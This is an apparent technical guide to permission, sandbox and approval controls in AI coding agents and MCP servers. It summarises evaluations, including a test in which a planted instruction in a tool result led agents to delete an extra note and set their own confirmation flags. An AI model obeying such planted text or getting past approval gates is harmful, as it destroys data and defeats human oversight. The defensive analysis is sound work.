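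Claude Code refuses a tool call if either the developer's user settings or the project's settings deny the tool, even if the other settings allow it. Anyone can therefore add a restriction that another person's allow rule won't cancel.

But developers can add allow rules for anything that no one else has denied or marked as ask. If an administrator lists five approved sites in managed settings and writes nothing else, a developer can approve a sixth. The administrator can prevent this with `allowManagedPermissionRulesOnly`, which makes managed settings the only settings source for permission rules. Claude Code then ignores deny rules in project files too, so if a project has a deny rule to protect its deployment tool, the administrator would need to copy that rule into managed settings. Administrators can also use managed settings to restrict which MCP servers developers can use.

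A company that delivers its settings from Anthropic's servers should also plan for a failed download. By default, Claude Code doesn't wait for fresh settings when it starts, so it may run with a stored copy or none. If `forceRemoteSettingsRefresh` is set, it exits when it can't fetch them.

Allow rules in shared project files need a separate check because a stranger could have written them. Claude Code applies a project's allow rules only after the developer accepts a trust dialog that lists them, but it applies deny and ask rules immediately. Scripted runs never show the dialog, so allow rules that work on a developer's laptop may have no effect in an automated build unless someone has already marked the folder as trusted.

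A mod, which is a plugin that runs its own code inside Claude Code, can also approve a call that a deny rule would refuse. Managed settings, or a Team or Enterprise login for the session, prevent this by default. An individual developer who has neither and relies on deny rules should review mods as carefully as the rules.

### When an organisation marks a connector tool as "ask"

An organisation can mark an individual connector tool as "ask" in claude.ai. If that setting reaches a Claude Code session, it overrides a developer's allow rule for the tool, and Claude Code prompts for approval before every call, even in auto mode and in `bypassPermissions` mode, which otherwise skips permission prompts. In `dontAsk` mode, Claude Code blocks the call.

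Suppose a developer has allowed every tool from a connected customer database, but the organisation has marked the database's `update_record` tool as "ask". The agent can read records without a prompt, but the developer has to approve each update, even if a hook approves calls automatically.

This lets the organisation require approval for a sensitive action without blocking the whole connector. But Anthropic says the setting applies only in sessions that receive it, so an administrator should try a harmless update before relying on it. If developers can also connect to the database through a separately installed MCP server, the administrator needs an ask rule for that server too.

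### Where tool rules need the sandbox

Neither a limit on the fetch tool nor a rule on command text covers every program that can use the network. Anthropic says a deny or ask rule for a shell command covers the form of the command Claude usually writes but isn't a security boundary around the program. In its Claude Code guidance, the University of Vermont gives a similar warning about secret files, which both the file tools and shell commands can reach.

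A team that needs a firm limit on where commands can connect should use the sandbox. By default, though, Claude Code runs commands without the sandbox if it can't start, so turning it on is not enough. The agent may also retry a failed command outside the sandbox. In Manual mode, the retry normally needs approval, but an existing allow rule for the command also approves the retry, so a rule added weeks earlier could let the command run without network limits.

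An administrator can close these gaps in managed settings:

- `sandbox.enabled` set to `true` turns on the sandbox.
- `failIfUnavailable` set to `true` stops Claude Code from starting if the sandbox can't run.
- `allowUnsandboxedCommands` set to `false` prevents retries outside the sandbox.
- `allowManagedDomainsOnly` set to `true` limits sandboxed commands to the company's domains.

Developers can still exclude commands from the sandbox in their user settings, and Anthropic has no managed setting that prevents this. If a company wants one network limit that also covers the fetch tool and MCP servers, Anthropic recommends running the whole Claude Code process inside a container, a virtual machine or its separate sandbox program.

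## Browser control: VS Code and browser extensions

A web fetch only returns the content of a page, but an agent that controls a browser can also click buttons, type into fields, submit forms and open other pages. If the user is signed in to a site, the site treats the agent's actions as the user's own. An agent in a developer's browser could change a setting in a cloud console or reply to a customer without an API token, so limits on the team's tokens would not stop it.

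A common use of browser control is checking a staging site, a private copy of a web application where a team tests changes before release. A fetch can show that a new sign-up form is on the page, but the agent has to fill in and submit the form to find out whether it rejects a bad email address. A rule that only permits reading would prevent this check.

### VS Code's built-in browser

VS Code has its own browser that an agent can operate. The browser tools became generally available on 1 July 2026, when GitHub (2026) announced that they would be on by default. Microsoft's *Use browser tools with agents* lists tools for opening pages, reading their content, taking screenshots, clicking, typing and handling dialogs. Another tool, `runPlaywrightCode`, runs a script written for Playwright, a browser automation library. One script can contain many clicks and form entries, so a developer has to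 read the code to know what they are approving.

By default, the agent can't read or use tabs that the developer opened. When it opens a page itself, VS Code starts a temporary session without cookies or stored data from other tabs, so the agent is not signed in. For a task that needs a login, the developer can select "Share with Agent" on an open tab and confirm. The agent can then use the tab's existing session, including its sign-in state, until the developer revokes access. In Autopilot, a mode in which the agent works without waiting for answers, VS Code declines the agent's requests for a shared tab.

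Sharing a tab may give the agent access to more than the page it shows. According to Microsoft's *Integrated browser*, local browsing uses global storage by default, which keeps logins across all tabs and workspaces. The agent also has a navigation tool, so a team should assume the agent could go from the shared staging page to another site where the developer is signed in. Setting `workbench.browser.dataStorage` to `ephemeral` keeps each tab's data separate. The developer can then sign in to the staging site with a test account and share only that tab.

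### Offering a tool and approving its use

Microsoft treats making a tool available and approving a particular use of it as separate decisions. A developer offers the browser tools by selecting them for a session, and an administrator can turn them off with the `BrowserChatTools` policy. If the tools are available, the permission level helps determine which calls run unasked. Microsoft's *Manage approvals and permissions* describes three levels for sessions in the Copilot harness:

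- Manual permissions asks about actions that the developer's approval settings don't already cover.
- Assisted permissions lets a model assess each call and asks the developer about those it doesn't approve.
- Allow all runs every call without asking.

Sessions in a separate Git worktree always use Allow all, so a developer who chooses a worktree to keep code changes apart also loses the prompts for browser actions.

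A team can mark a tool as ineligible for automatic approval, but this doesn't guarantee a prompt in Copilot sessions. Microsoft's *Manage AI settings in enterprise environments* warns that the setting only removes the Allow all level in those sessions. Assisted permissions and saved session approvals can still approve the tool. If an agent doesn't need to run page scripts, withholding `runPlaywrightCode` is safer than relying on a prompt. The team should confirm that the tool is unavailable, since Microsoft's *Secure development with AI in VS Code* notes that developers can't deselect every built-in tool.

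### What VS Code's URL rules cover

Copilot's built-in fetch tool has its own approvals. When the agent tries to fetch from a new host, the developer can allow the request once, for the session or permanently. An approval for `https://example.com` doesn't cover the unencrypted `http` address or any subdomain.

Approving the address only permits contact with the site. Microsoft says the developer gets no second prompt to review the response before the model uses it, so any instruction planted in the page reaches the model unreviewed.

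An older harness, Local, prompts for approval once for the request and again for the response. Microsoft has deprecated it and plans to remove it by February 2027. Teams that have set `approveResponse` to `false` in Local's settings shouldn't expect a response prompt in Copilot sessions.

The second prompt probably gave little protection anyway, because few people would read a long documentation page closely enough to find one hostile sentence. A developer is more likely to notice the problem when the agent next asks to do something, because the request shows a specific command, address or form.

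Administrators can also restrict domains through a network filter, but it doesn't cover every route equally.

| Route to a site | Controls in a Copilot session |
|---|---|
| Built-in fetch | URL approvals and the filter's allowlist |
| VS Code's browser | The filter's allowlist and denylist |
| Terminal command | Command approvals and, if turned on, the sandbox |

In the browser, a denied domain takes precedence over an allowed one. For fetches, Microsoft says only that a non-empty allowlist blocks any domain not on it, even under Allow all. A team that lists only denied domains should therefore test whether that list blocks fetches.

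The terminal sandbox has its own network settings, so a team has to restrict commands' network access there too. Developers need to restart VS Code after changing the filter so that new browser sessions use the updated lists.

### Claude in Chrome

Claude Code can also work in the developer's own browser through Anthropic's extension, Claude in Chrome. The agent opens new tabs, but Anthropic says it shares the browser's login state, so it can use any site where the developer is signed in. The developer therefore has to keep the agent away from accounts it shouldn't use, whereas in VS Code's browser the agent can use a signed-in tab only if the developer shares it.

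The Claude in Chrome extension manages permissions by site. According to Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide*, a user can allow one action, always allow actions on the site, or decline. Even on a site marked "always allow", Claude asks before it downloads a file, enters potentially sensitive information or grants an authorization. Changing permission settings needs explicit approval in every mode.

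Anthropic also lists actions that Claude may not take, regardless of permissions. These include making purchases, creating accounts, permanently deleting files or messages, and following instructions found in emails or web content. Anthropic's *Use Claude in Chrome safely* adds that Claude can't open adult sites or known piracy sites and asks before opening financial ones. Anthropic says it has probably not identified every site in these categories.

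A team should test these limits with harmless actions before relying on them. The permissions guide says Claude asks before entering sensitive data, but the safety page lists entering it as prohibited. Neither page lists publishing a post or sending a message as an action Claude always asks about first.

In Claude Code's auto mode, when the automated reviewer approves a browser call, the extension skips its own check for that site, unless the permission rules deny any site to the extension. The agent therefore isn't limited to the developer's list of approved sites. In VS Code sessions that connect to Chrome at startup, however, Claude Code still asks about sites the developer hasn't allowed, until the developer types `@browser`.

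Owners of Team and Enterprise accounts can set a firmer limit with an allowlist of sites Claude may use and a blocklist that applies regardless of other settings, according to Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome admin controls*. The extension is normally on by default for these plans, and Anthropic recommends starting with a restrictive allowlist.

A permitted site can still expose or receive private data. Claude takes screenshots to see a page, so anything visible in the tab, such as customer names on a staging site, becomes part of the conversation. Claude can also upload files from the developer's machine. A Claude Code rule that denies reading a file also blocks its upload. From version 2.1.293, Claude refuses to upload files with typical credential names such as `.env`, but a name check would not catch a password saved in `notes.txt`.

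OpenAI lets administrators control some of these powers separately. According to OpenAI's *Codex Chrome extension* page, Codex asks before using each new website, and OpenAI recommends the in-app browser for local servers and public pages that need no login. According to *Manage browser and computer use in your Enterprise workspace*, administrators can block all sites by default, add exceptions, and set separate rules for uploads, downloads and debugging access. They can also stop members from saving "Always allow" approvals. A team could use these rules to let Codex test the staging site but not upload files to it.

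### The Trajectory Labs evaluation

In July 2026, Anthropic commissioned an outside company, Trajectory Labs, to test how often prompt injections succeeded against Claude Code and Codex. The company wrote 72 scenarios, kept them from Anthropic and ran each ten times. An attack counted as successful if it led to an action that would have caused irreversible harm outside the test, such as leaking sensitive data or committing financial fraud.

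Both products used the same browser integration, a set of MCP tools that Trajectory Labs built around common Chrome functions. Anthropic's reported results are consistent with 720 attempts per model in each mode.

| Model | Permission mode | Attacks that succeeded | Count implied by the rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 and Sonnet 5 | Claude Code, auto mode | 0% | 0 of 2,160 |
| The same three models | Claude Code, `bypassPermissions` | 0.09% on average | 2 of 2,160 |
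| GPT-5.6 Sol | Codex, Auto-review | 5.83% | 42 of 720 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Codex, Full Access | 19.03% | 137 of 720 |

Most of the difference between the products existed without an automated reviewer. Even with permission checks bypassed, the Claude models resisted nearly every attack, so auto mode had only about two successful attacks left to prevent. The test therefore shows little about how much auto mode adds. For GPT-5.6 Sol, about 70% fewer attacks succeeded under Auto-review than under Full Access, but Full Access also removes limits on files and the network.

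The overall rates also combine tasks where the tools returned text with tasks where the agent worked through screenshots. Success rates differed between the two, and Anthropic reported higher rates for OpenAI models on browser tasks. One plausible reason for such a gap is that a text filter would miss text in a screenshot, which reaches the model as part of an image. A team whose agent works mainly from screenshots shouldn't treat 5.83% as an estimate of its own risk.

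Zero successes also don't prove that the risk is zero. If the 720 attempts against one model had been independent, the 95% upper confidence limit on the true success rate would be about 0.4%. But each scenario was run ten times, and repeated runs don't count as different attacks. Counting each scenario once raises the limit to about 4%.

Trajectory Labs had also optimised the attacks against an earlier model, Claude Opus 4.7, whereas a real attacker could adapt them to the model in use. Attackers succeeded against Opus 5 in 2.0% of cases after 15 attempts in a general injection test by the security firm Gray Swan, according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*.

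Anthropic commissioned the test, published the results and sells one of the products compared. The test left out the safeguards in both companies' browser extensions. In an earlier internal Anthropic test with an adaptive attacker, the improved safeguards in Anthropic's extension reduced the attack success rate against Opus 4.5 from 8.0% for the model alone to 1.4%. OpenAI released a new version of Auto-review shortly before Anthropic published its article, so the Codex figure may be out of date.

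The evaluation gives Codex users a reason to prefer Auto-review to Full Access. It is much weaker evidence for letting any of these agents use a browser signed in to email, banking or production systems, where one successful attack could do serious damage.

### Trying three rules on a staging site

Suppose a team wants its agent to check a new sign-up form at `staging.example.com`, which is behind a login. The team considers giving the agent a separate browser profile, limiting it to listed sites, and requiring approval before it submits a form, buys something, publishes content or changes permissions.

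Installing the extension in a new Chrome profile works well. The developer signs in there only to the staging site, with a test account. If a page on that site tells the agent to open the developer's email, the agent reaches a login screen, even if neither the model nor a person notices the attack.

This protection is weaker if staging uses the company's single sign-on, because the same login may open other services. A test account that exists only on staging avoids this problem. The agent can still reach internal pages that require no login if the browser is on the company network.

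For VS Code's browser, the site list could look like this:

```json
{
  "chat.agent.networkFilter": true,
  "chat.agent.allowedNetworkDomains": ["staging.example.com"]
}
```

An administrator should set the matching policies so that developers can't change the list. The full hostname is safer than `*.example.com`, which could also allow the production admin site. The team may need to add the host that handles sign-in, and should check that pages still load properly with the filter on.

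The list keeps the agent's browser on the staging site, but that site may contain a copy of production data, including customer comments, and may send real emails when someone submits a form. Filling the site with invented data and turning off outgoing email deal with both problems.

Approval before every submission is a poor fit. The agent has to submit valid, invalid and duplicate entries, which could mean a dozen nearly identical prompts. The rule is also hard to write, because VS Code's `clickElement` tool presses a Submit button in the same way as it opens a menu. The team can set its approvals by site and account instead:

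| Action | On staging, with the test account | On any other site |
|---|---|---|
| Submit a form | Allow | Ask |
| Make a purchase | Run a scripted test with a fake payment | Deny |
| Publish | Allow if the public can't see it | Ask |
| Change permissions | Ask | Deny |

This is the policy to aim for, but no product described here can enforce the whole table. The site list should prevent most of the cases in the last column. For the rest, the team can restrict what the test account can do.

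The extension's fixed prohibitions may also prevent the agent from finishing the sign-up check. Claude in Chrome is not allowed to create accounts, and Anthropic describes no exception for test sites. Microsoft, by contrast, gives testing a sign-up flow as an example task for VS Code's browser. A team using Claude in Chrome could have the agent check the error messages and leave account creation to a Playwright test in the repository.

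A person must approve permission changes, even on staging. The agent can submit and publish without asking because its test account has limited permissions, and that reason no longer holds if the agent can make the account an administrator.

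## MCP servers: who asks before a destructive call

Anyone can write an MCP server, and its author decides what the tools do and can change them later, whereas the browser tools in VS Code and Claude in Chrome are written by the companies that ship them. A team therefore has to decide whether developers may connect a particular server, and then which of its tools the agent may call without asking. For example, a team might let developers connect an issue tracker but still want a person to confirm before the agent deletes a project.

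Rules about tools can't replace a check on the server itself. A local MCP server is a program that the host starts on the developer's machine, using a command from a configuration file. That program can read files or contact the internet as soon as it starts, before the agent calls any of its tools.

Some hosts let developers install a local server by clicking a link. Delimarsky (2025) warned in *MCP Client Security Requirements for Local Server Installation* that an attacker could put any command in such a link and that a host might run it without showing it to the user. The proposal, now final, requires hosts with this feature to display the whole command, warn that it may be dangerous and wait for the user to agree. Users may still approve a malicious command, as Delimarsky acknowledges, so a company has good reason to let an administrator decide which servers developers can add.

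### Docker checks the server and the call separately

Docker's MCP gateway passes requests between agents and MCP servers. Docker's *MCP access policies* explains how an organisation can control the gateway with rules written in Cedar, a language for access policies. Docker applies the rules when a developer registers a server and when an agent uses it, but a rule for one doesn't cover the other.

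Docker denies anything that no rule permits, and a matching `forbid` rule overrides every `permit`. A team could write this policy for its issue tracker:

```cedar
permit (principal, action == MCP::Action::"register", resource)
when {
  resource in MCP::Server::"tracker" &&
  resource.identityURL == "https://mcp.example.org/tracker"
};

permit (principal, action == MCP::Action::"invokeTool", resource)
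when { resource in MCP::Server::"tracker" && resource.readOnly == true };

@requireApproval("This call can change the tracker")
permit (principal, action == MCP::Action::"invokeTool", resource)
when { resource in MCP::Server::"tracker" && resource.readOnly == false };
```

| Request | Result |
|---|---|
| Register the listed address as `tracker` | Goes through |
| Register another address as `tracker` | Denied |
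| Register the listed address as `issues` | Denied |
| Call a tool labelled read-only | Runs |
| Call a tool with no label | Needs confirmation |
| Read a resource, such as a stored document, from the server | Denied, because no rule permits it |

The registration rule checks both the server's name and its address because the rules for tool calls identify the server only by its registered name. If the registration rule checked only the name, a developer could register a different server as `tracker`, and the agent could use that server with the permissions meant for the real one.

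The gateway sends the user a new confirmation prompt, through the host, for each call that needs one. The prompt names the server and gives the reason from the policy, but it leaves out the call's arguments. A developer would see that the agent is trying to change the tracker, but not which project. An agent running unattended could also answer the prompt automatically, so Docker advises administrators to use `forbid` for operations that must never run.

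To withdraw a server, an administrator must forbid both registering it and using it. A ban on registration stops new developers from adding the server, but anyone who registered it earlier can keep using it. The ban on use must cover every name that developers have given the server.

Local servers run outside Docker's sandbox, so the policy can control the agent's calls to them but not what the servers do on the machine. An administrator can refuse to register local servers. The gateway permits all MCP activity for users who don't have enforcement turned on, so administrators may want to check that the policy applies to everyone.

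### How Codex and Claude Code recognise a server

OpenAI says that if an administrator sets a list of approved MCP servers, Codex enables a server only when both its name and its identity match an entry. The identity is a command for a local server and a URL for a remote one. In *Restrict MCP servers from requirements.toml*, the note that accompanied the code for this list, gt-oai explained that requiring both prevents users from getting around the list by renaming a server. An empty list disables every MCP server.

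Claude Code users can connect any server they choose unless an administrator restricts them. Anthropic reviews the connectors in its own directory against listing criteria but does not audit any MCP server for security. An administrator can deploy a file called `managed-mcp.json`, which generally limits Claude Code to the servers it contains, or can filter the servers that developers add themselves. For example:

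```json
{
  "allowManagedMcpServersOnly": true,
  "allowedMcpServers": [
    { "serverCommand": ["npx", "-y", "@example/tracker-mcp@1.4.2"] },
    { "serverUrl": "https://mcp.example.com/*" }
  ]
}
```

The command entry allows one local server, a JavaScript package that `npx` downloads and runs. The URL entry allows remote servers at one host. A separate `deniedMcpServers` list overrides both.

Claude Code can also match a server by name alone, but Anthropic warns that this is not a security control, since a user can name any server `github`. GitHub's *MCP allowlists in enterprise managed settings* (2026) describes the lists that GitHub released for Copilot in August. They use the same two keys and also accept URLs, exact commands and names.

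Without the first line of the example, Claude Code merges allowlists from every settings file, including the developer's own. The setting that makes managed permission rules exclusive does not apply to server allowlists, so an administrator who sets only that one would control which tools developers can approve but not which servers they can add.

A denied-URL entry for `https://staging.example.com/*` blocks servers only on the standard HTTPS port, so a server on port 8443 of the same host would still load. The entry `*://staging.example.com:*/*` covers every port and scheme.

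The allowlist doesn't apply to some built-in servers, including Claude in Chrome. A company that wants to block Claude in Chrome needs to add it to the denylist.

### When an approved server changes

Suppose an administrator reviews version 1.4.2 of the tracker package and approves the command `npx -y @example/tracker-mcp`. Because the command gives no version, `npx` can later download a newer release that nobody on the team has reviewed. Someone who buys the package from its author, or steals the author's publishing account, could publish a release that copies every issue to a stranger. The approval would still cover that release because the command hasn't changed.

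Adding the version to the command fixes this. Claude Code compares every argument in order, so the entry in the example covers only `@1.4.2`. When a developer changes the version, the approval no longer applies, and the administrator can review the new release before updating the entry. Pinning the server's version doesn't necessarily pin its dependencies, so a team that needs more certainty should install a reviewed copy that includes them.

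OpenAI's documented entries contain only a command, with no place for arguments. If Codex compares only the program name, an entry for `npx` would accept any package that a developer lists under the approved server name. Teams using Codex should test how it matches entries, or install the server as its own program and approve the full path.

In the same note, gt-oai acknowledged that approving a program by its full path doesn't stop someone from replacing it with a malicious one. Codex could detect the change by storing a hash, a short fingerprint of the file's contents, but gt-oai left that out because it would break updates, since each one would change the hash and require a new approval. For a server with production credentials, it's reasonable to require approval after every update.

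| Change after approval | Codex's list | Claude Code's list, matched by command or URL |
|---|---|---|
| Another server takes the approved name | Blocked | Blocked |
| The command requests a new package version | No documented check | Blocked until the administrator updates the entry |
| Someone replaces the program at the approved path | Allowed | Allowed |
| The operator updates a remote server at the same URL | Allowed | Allowed |

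Claude Code also ignores environment variables when it compares commands, although some can change what a JavaScript program loads at startup. An administrator who needs to lock these values can define the server in `managed-mcp.json`.

A remote server's URL usually stays the same when its code changes. The team can save a copy of the server's tool list and review new tools or changed descriptions, but that won't reveal an update that changes only what an existing tool does. The team is therefore trusting whoever operates the server, and should give the server a token with a narrow scope.

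VS Code can ask the developer again about some servers after their configuration changes. But Microsoft says servers in a project's configuration files inherit Workspace Trust, the developer's earlier decision to trust the project folder. A pull request could therefore add a server that starts without a separate prompt, so reviewers should treat a change to `.vscode/mcp.json` as a request to run new code.

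### What the MCP specification requires

Approving a server does not determine who confirms a dangerous call. *Tools* (2026), the part of the Model Context Protocol specification that covers tool calls, states that there "SHOULD always be a human in the loop" who can deny them. In technical standards, SHOULD marks a recommendation, not a requirement, so a host that never prompts can still comply with the specification.

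The specification also recommends that hosts show users a tool's inputs before sending them to the server, to avoid exfiltration. For example, a user could see from the inputs, but not from the tool's name, that an agent is about to put a customer list in a support ticket.

To decide when to prompt, a host can use tool annotations, the labels that a server puts on its own tools. In a March post, Model Context Protocol (2026) lists four that describe behaviour:

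| Annotation | Meaning when true | Value if the server gives none |
|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool doesn't change anything | False |
| `destructiveHint` | Its changes may be destructive, not just additions | True |
| `idempotentHint` | Repeating the same call is safe | False |
| `openWorldHint` | The tool deals with outside systems or people | True |

A tool with no labels therefore counts as able to make destructive changes and reach outside systems. Server authors don't have to label their tools, and a host that follows these defaults will treat unlabeled ones with caution.

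The author of a malicious server can annotate a deletion tool as read-only. The specification requires hosts to treat annotations as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. When the protocol's designers discussed the first proposal, co-creator Justin Spahr-Summers asked how a host could use annotations that couldn't be trusted. Another participant, Basil Hosmer, argued that hosts should ignore annotations from untrusted servers. The designers settled on calling every annotation a hint and leaving its weight up to each host.

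I think a host can safely act on a label that calls for more caution, even if it comes from an unknown server. If a tool is wrongly labeled destructive, the user at worst sees an unnecessary prompt. A read-only label needs to come from a trusted server, because believing a false one could let a deletion run without approval.

Even an accurate label describes only one tool, while Willison's lethal trifecta can come from several tools in one session. The March post lists five open proposals for new or related annotations, including one by GitHub and OpenAI on trust and sensitivity. Such labels could let a host tighten its approval rules after the agent reads text from outsiders, but they couldn't guarantee that data stays private. The post leaves that to sandboxes and network controls.

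### Elicitation and what happens when it fails

A server can also request confirmation itself through elicitation, a question that the host relays to the user. Under Model Context Protocol's *Elicitation* (2026), the exchange for a database deletion would work like this:

1. The host sends the agent's call and declares which kinds of elicitation it supports.
2. The server replies that it needs more input and supplies a question for the user.
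3. The host shows the question and makes clear which server sent it.
4. The user accepts, declines or dismisses the question.
5. The host repeats the call with the answer, and the server decides whether to delete the database.

The server can send the question as a form or as a web address for the user to open. If it needs a password or access token, it must use a web page instead of a form, so that the secret doesn't pass through the host or the model.

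If the host doesn't support elicitation, the server can't ask the user to approve a destructive call. The specification requires servers to handle failed elicitation requests but doesn't specify whether the call should then run (fail-open) or stop (fail-closed).

Developers of MCP servers and hosts often leave confirmation to each other. *When Neither Side Confirms* (Yao, Yang et al., 2026) gives the example of a server for the mapping program QGIS, which skips its own confirmation by default because, according to its documentation, "MCP clients gate destructive tool calls themselves". If a developer connects it to a host that doesn't prompt the user, destructive calls run without anyone confirming them.

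### How often neither side asks

Yao and colleagues measured how common this is by reading source code on both sides. They started with the official MCP registry and found 17,554 suitable GitHub repositories in Python, TypeScript or JavaScript. They sampled 1,000 of these: the 200 with the most stars and 800 chosen at random from the rest. Each random repository counted as about 22 in the estimates.

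A program found 16,711 tools in the sample and flagged 1,995 as possibly destructive. The researchers set aside 100 used to develop the program, then drew 366 tools. Two language models classified each one independently, and a third settled disagreements. They classified 269 of the 366 as destructive, meaning that a call could permanently delete or overwrite data, send messages, move money or run arbitrary commands.

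A separate check of 40 repositories showed that the program had failed to flag 83% of their destructive tools. The researchers added these missed tools to their estimate:

| Confirmation by the server | Estimated share of destructive tools |
|---|---|
| None, and no destructive label | 70% |
| A destructive label only | 20% |
| A flag or token that the model can supply itself | 8.9% |
| A question to the user, but the call runs if the host can't relay it | 0.2% |
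| A human answer, without which the tool refuses | 0.5% |

The first two rows give the paper's main result for servers, which is that an estimated 90% of destructive tools have no server-side confirmation (95% confidence interval: 82% to 95%). The split between those two rows is much less certain, with an interval of 43% to 88% for tools with neither a confirmation nor a label.

Few servers used elicitation, and most of those that did could still act without an answer. In 19 repositories, 168 tools asked the user by default before a destructive action. If the host couldn't relay the question, 30 of those tools ran anyway, 100 accepted a flag that the model could set, and 38 refused.

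The researchers also examined 41 open-source hosts: 25 applications and 16 SDKs (software kits for building agents). In a default setup, 32 had no approval step for an ordinary MCP call. These were all 16 SDKs and 16 of the applications, including Cline, Goose and OpenHands.

Seven of the 25 applications, including VS Code, Gemini CLI and Zed, asked the user before ordinary calls, although VS Code skipped this for tools labelled read-only and servers in its sandbox. Codex decided based on annotations, and Qwen Code used a model. In total, 9 of the 25 (36%) had a blocking approval step, if Qwen Code's automated check counts. This is close to an earlier result the researchers cite from Majeed and colleagues, who found such a step in 37.2% of MCP client applications on GitHub.

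The researchers then paired each of the 269 destructive tools with every host and worked out what, if anything, would require approval before the call. The call would run without enforced approval in 60.7% of the pairs with applications, and in 74.9% of pairs when SDKs were included.

Adding seven closed-source applications, including Claude Code and Cursor, lowered the application figure from 60.7% across 25 applications to 47.5% across 32. The seven must have added almost no unapproved pairs, because the figure would have fallen to about 47.4% if they had added none. A team should check its own host's default before worrying about the average.

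A low figure for unapproved calls doesn't necessarily mean that a person sees the rest. The figure excludes calls that Qwen Code's model would decide, which are in a separate category. Claude Code's auto mode also lets a model decide unless an ask rule applies.

### What happened when agents ran the calls

To check their reading of the code, Yao and colleagues connected several hosts to a test server that could delete notes and asked each agent to delete one note. When the tool had only a destructive label, the coding agent opencode and four SDKs deleted it without an approval prompt. When the tool required a confirmation flag, the model set the flag itself.

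Crush and the interactive version of Codex showed an approval dialog before the call reached the server, and cancelling it prevented the deletion. In non-interactive mode, Codex refused the call because no one was available to approve it.

The researchers then tested prompt injection. The user asked the agent to list the notes and delete one, but the returned list also contained an instruction to delete a different one. They ran the attack 240 times on each of five low-cost models, spread across the four SDKs.

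| Model | Runs that deleted the extra note, of 240 |
|---|---|
| GPT-4o-mini | 215 |
| Qwen3.7-Flash | 153 |
| Mistral Small 2603 | 101 |
| Gemma 4 26B-A4B | 10 |
| DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash | 0 |

The paper's abstract reports 479 deletions in 960 runs, but that count excludes DeepSeek, the only model that never deleted the extra note. Across all five models, the attack succeeded in 40% of runs. Results varied little by SDK, with 105 to 126 deletions on each.

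When the tool had only a label, all 180 attempted deletions succeeded. Requiring a flag stopped some attempts, but even when the planted text didn't mention the flag, the models set it and completed 127 of 169 attempted deletions.

These attacks used inexpensive models and a simple test server, so 40% is not an estimate for the strongest coding agents. The runs do show that a confirmation flag is weak protection, because the server can check whether the model set `confirm=true` but not whether a person agreed. DeepSeek resisted every planted instruction, but for the deletion that the user had requested, it set the flag on its first call in 135 of 160 runs without asking the user to confirm.

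### What would close the gap

Yao and colleagues used the same pairs to calculate what would happen if hosts or servers changed their defaults. The figures below are for the 25 open-source applications.

| Default | Destructive pairs that run unapproved | Destructive pairs that the server refuses because it can't ask | Harmless flagged pairs in which the user has to answer |
|---|---|---|---|
| Current software | 60.7% | 0.7% | 32.5% |
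| Every host relays elicitation | 56.7% | 0.0% | 35.2% |
| Every host prompts unless a label marks the tool as safe | 5.4% | 0.7% | 82.6% |
| Every destructive tool refuses without a human answer | 0.0% | 71.0% | 32.5% |

Having every host relay elicitation requests would help little because few servers send them. Requiring an answer before every tool call would stop all unapproved calls, but most calls would then fail because most hosts can't relay the question. Some would fail even after the user had approved them in the host, because the server can't know about that approval. The paper suggests a new protocol feature that would let a host declare that it obtains human approval, so the server would need to refuse a call only when no one had asked the user.

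Prompting for every tool not labeled read-only or non-destructive would do much more. The remaining 5.4% comes from destructive tools that their servers give one of those labels. Including the destructive tools that the search program missed raises the remaining share to at least 10.6% across all 41 hosts. A host could catch some of these by skipping the prompt only for tools labeled read-only, but it would prompt more often.

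For tools that looked destructive but turned out to be harmless, the share of pairs with a prompt would rise from 32.5% to 82.6%. These percentages don't measure how often a developer would see a prompt, because people use some tools far more than others. They also leave out harmless tools that the program never flagged, including most ordinary reads, and many of those have no label and would need approval too. A team can reduce the number of prompts by allowing, by name, the read tools it uses every day.

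### How far to trust the figures

The paper is a preprint, and language models did much of the work of classifying the tools. Two people checked a sample of 60 tools without seeing the models' labels. Their labels matched the models' on the type of confirmation for 58 of them. On whether a tool was destructive, the labels matched for 51 of the 56 tools the two people felt sure about. In all five mismatches, the models had labeled something reversible or harmless, such as renaming a project, as destructive.

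This suggests that the models overcounted destructive tools. The researchers estimate that correcting for this would remove about 12% of those counted. The much larger problem is that the search program failed to flag 83% of destructive tools. The 90% estimate corrects for these unflagged tools, based on 40 repositories, but the 60.7% figure does not. Including them raises the figure for all 41 hosts from 74.9% to 77.3%. The paper gives no matching figure for applications alone.

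AI agents also traced the hosts' code, and a second agent from another company reached the same result for all 20 hosts it checked. The researchers ran seven hosts themselves. They classified the closed-source applications from documentation alone, so the evidence for the 47.5% figure is weaker than the evidence for the open-source result.

The percentages also describe possible combinations, not actual use. A little-known chat program counts as much as VS Code, and a tool nobody calls can count as much as one thousands of people use every day. Some teams will have turned on approvals, and some developers will have chosen "always allow". The study therefore doesn't measure how many destructive calls run unapproved in practice. Its finding that approval depends mainly on the host is much more reliable, because the gap between hosts that prompt and hosts that don't is far larger than any likely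 coding error.

### Defaults in Codex and Claude Managed Agents

Codex uses a tool's annotations to decide when to ask for approval. According to OpenAI, a tool labelled destructive always needs approval, even if the server also labels it read-only. Yao and colleagues found that Codex also asks about unlabelled tools. It skips approval for tools labelled read-only and not destructive, and for non-destructive tools that don't reach outside systems.

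Claude Managed Agents, Anthropic's service for running agents on its own platform, asks for approval before every MCP call by default. Anthropic's *Permission policies* explains that a server may add new tools, which shouldn't run without approval. The service doesn't ask before running its built-in tools.

Suppose the tracker's author adds `get_and_archive`, the tool from the earlier wildcard example, which returns an issue and then archives it:

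| Label on the new tool | Codex | Claude Managed Agents |
|---|---|---|
| None | Asks | Asks |
| Destructive | Asks | Asks |
| Read-only and not destructive | Runs | Asks |

The last row matters most because the server's author may have chosen the label by mistake or to avoid a prompt. Codex would run the tool, while Claude Managed Agents would wait for someone to approve it.

That protection depends on how the team reduces the prompts. Setting the whole server to `always_allow` would approve later additions too, like a wildcard in Claude Code, so the team should allow individual tools:

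```yaml
tools:
  - type: mcp_toolset
    mcp_server_name: tracker
    configs:
      - name: get_issue
        permission_policy:
          type: always_allow
```

The agent can now read issues without asking, but the default still applies to everything else. The session waits indefinitely for an answer, so a team that runs jobs overnight needs either to have someone available to respond or to remove the tools the job doesn't need.

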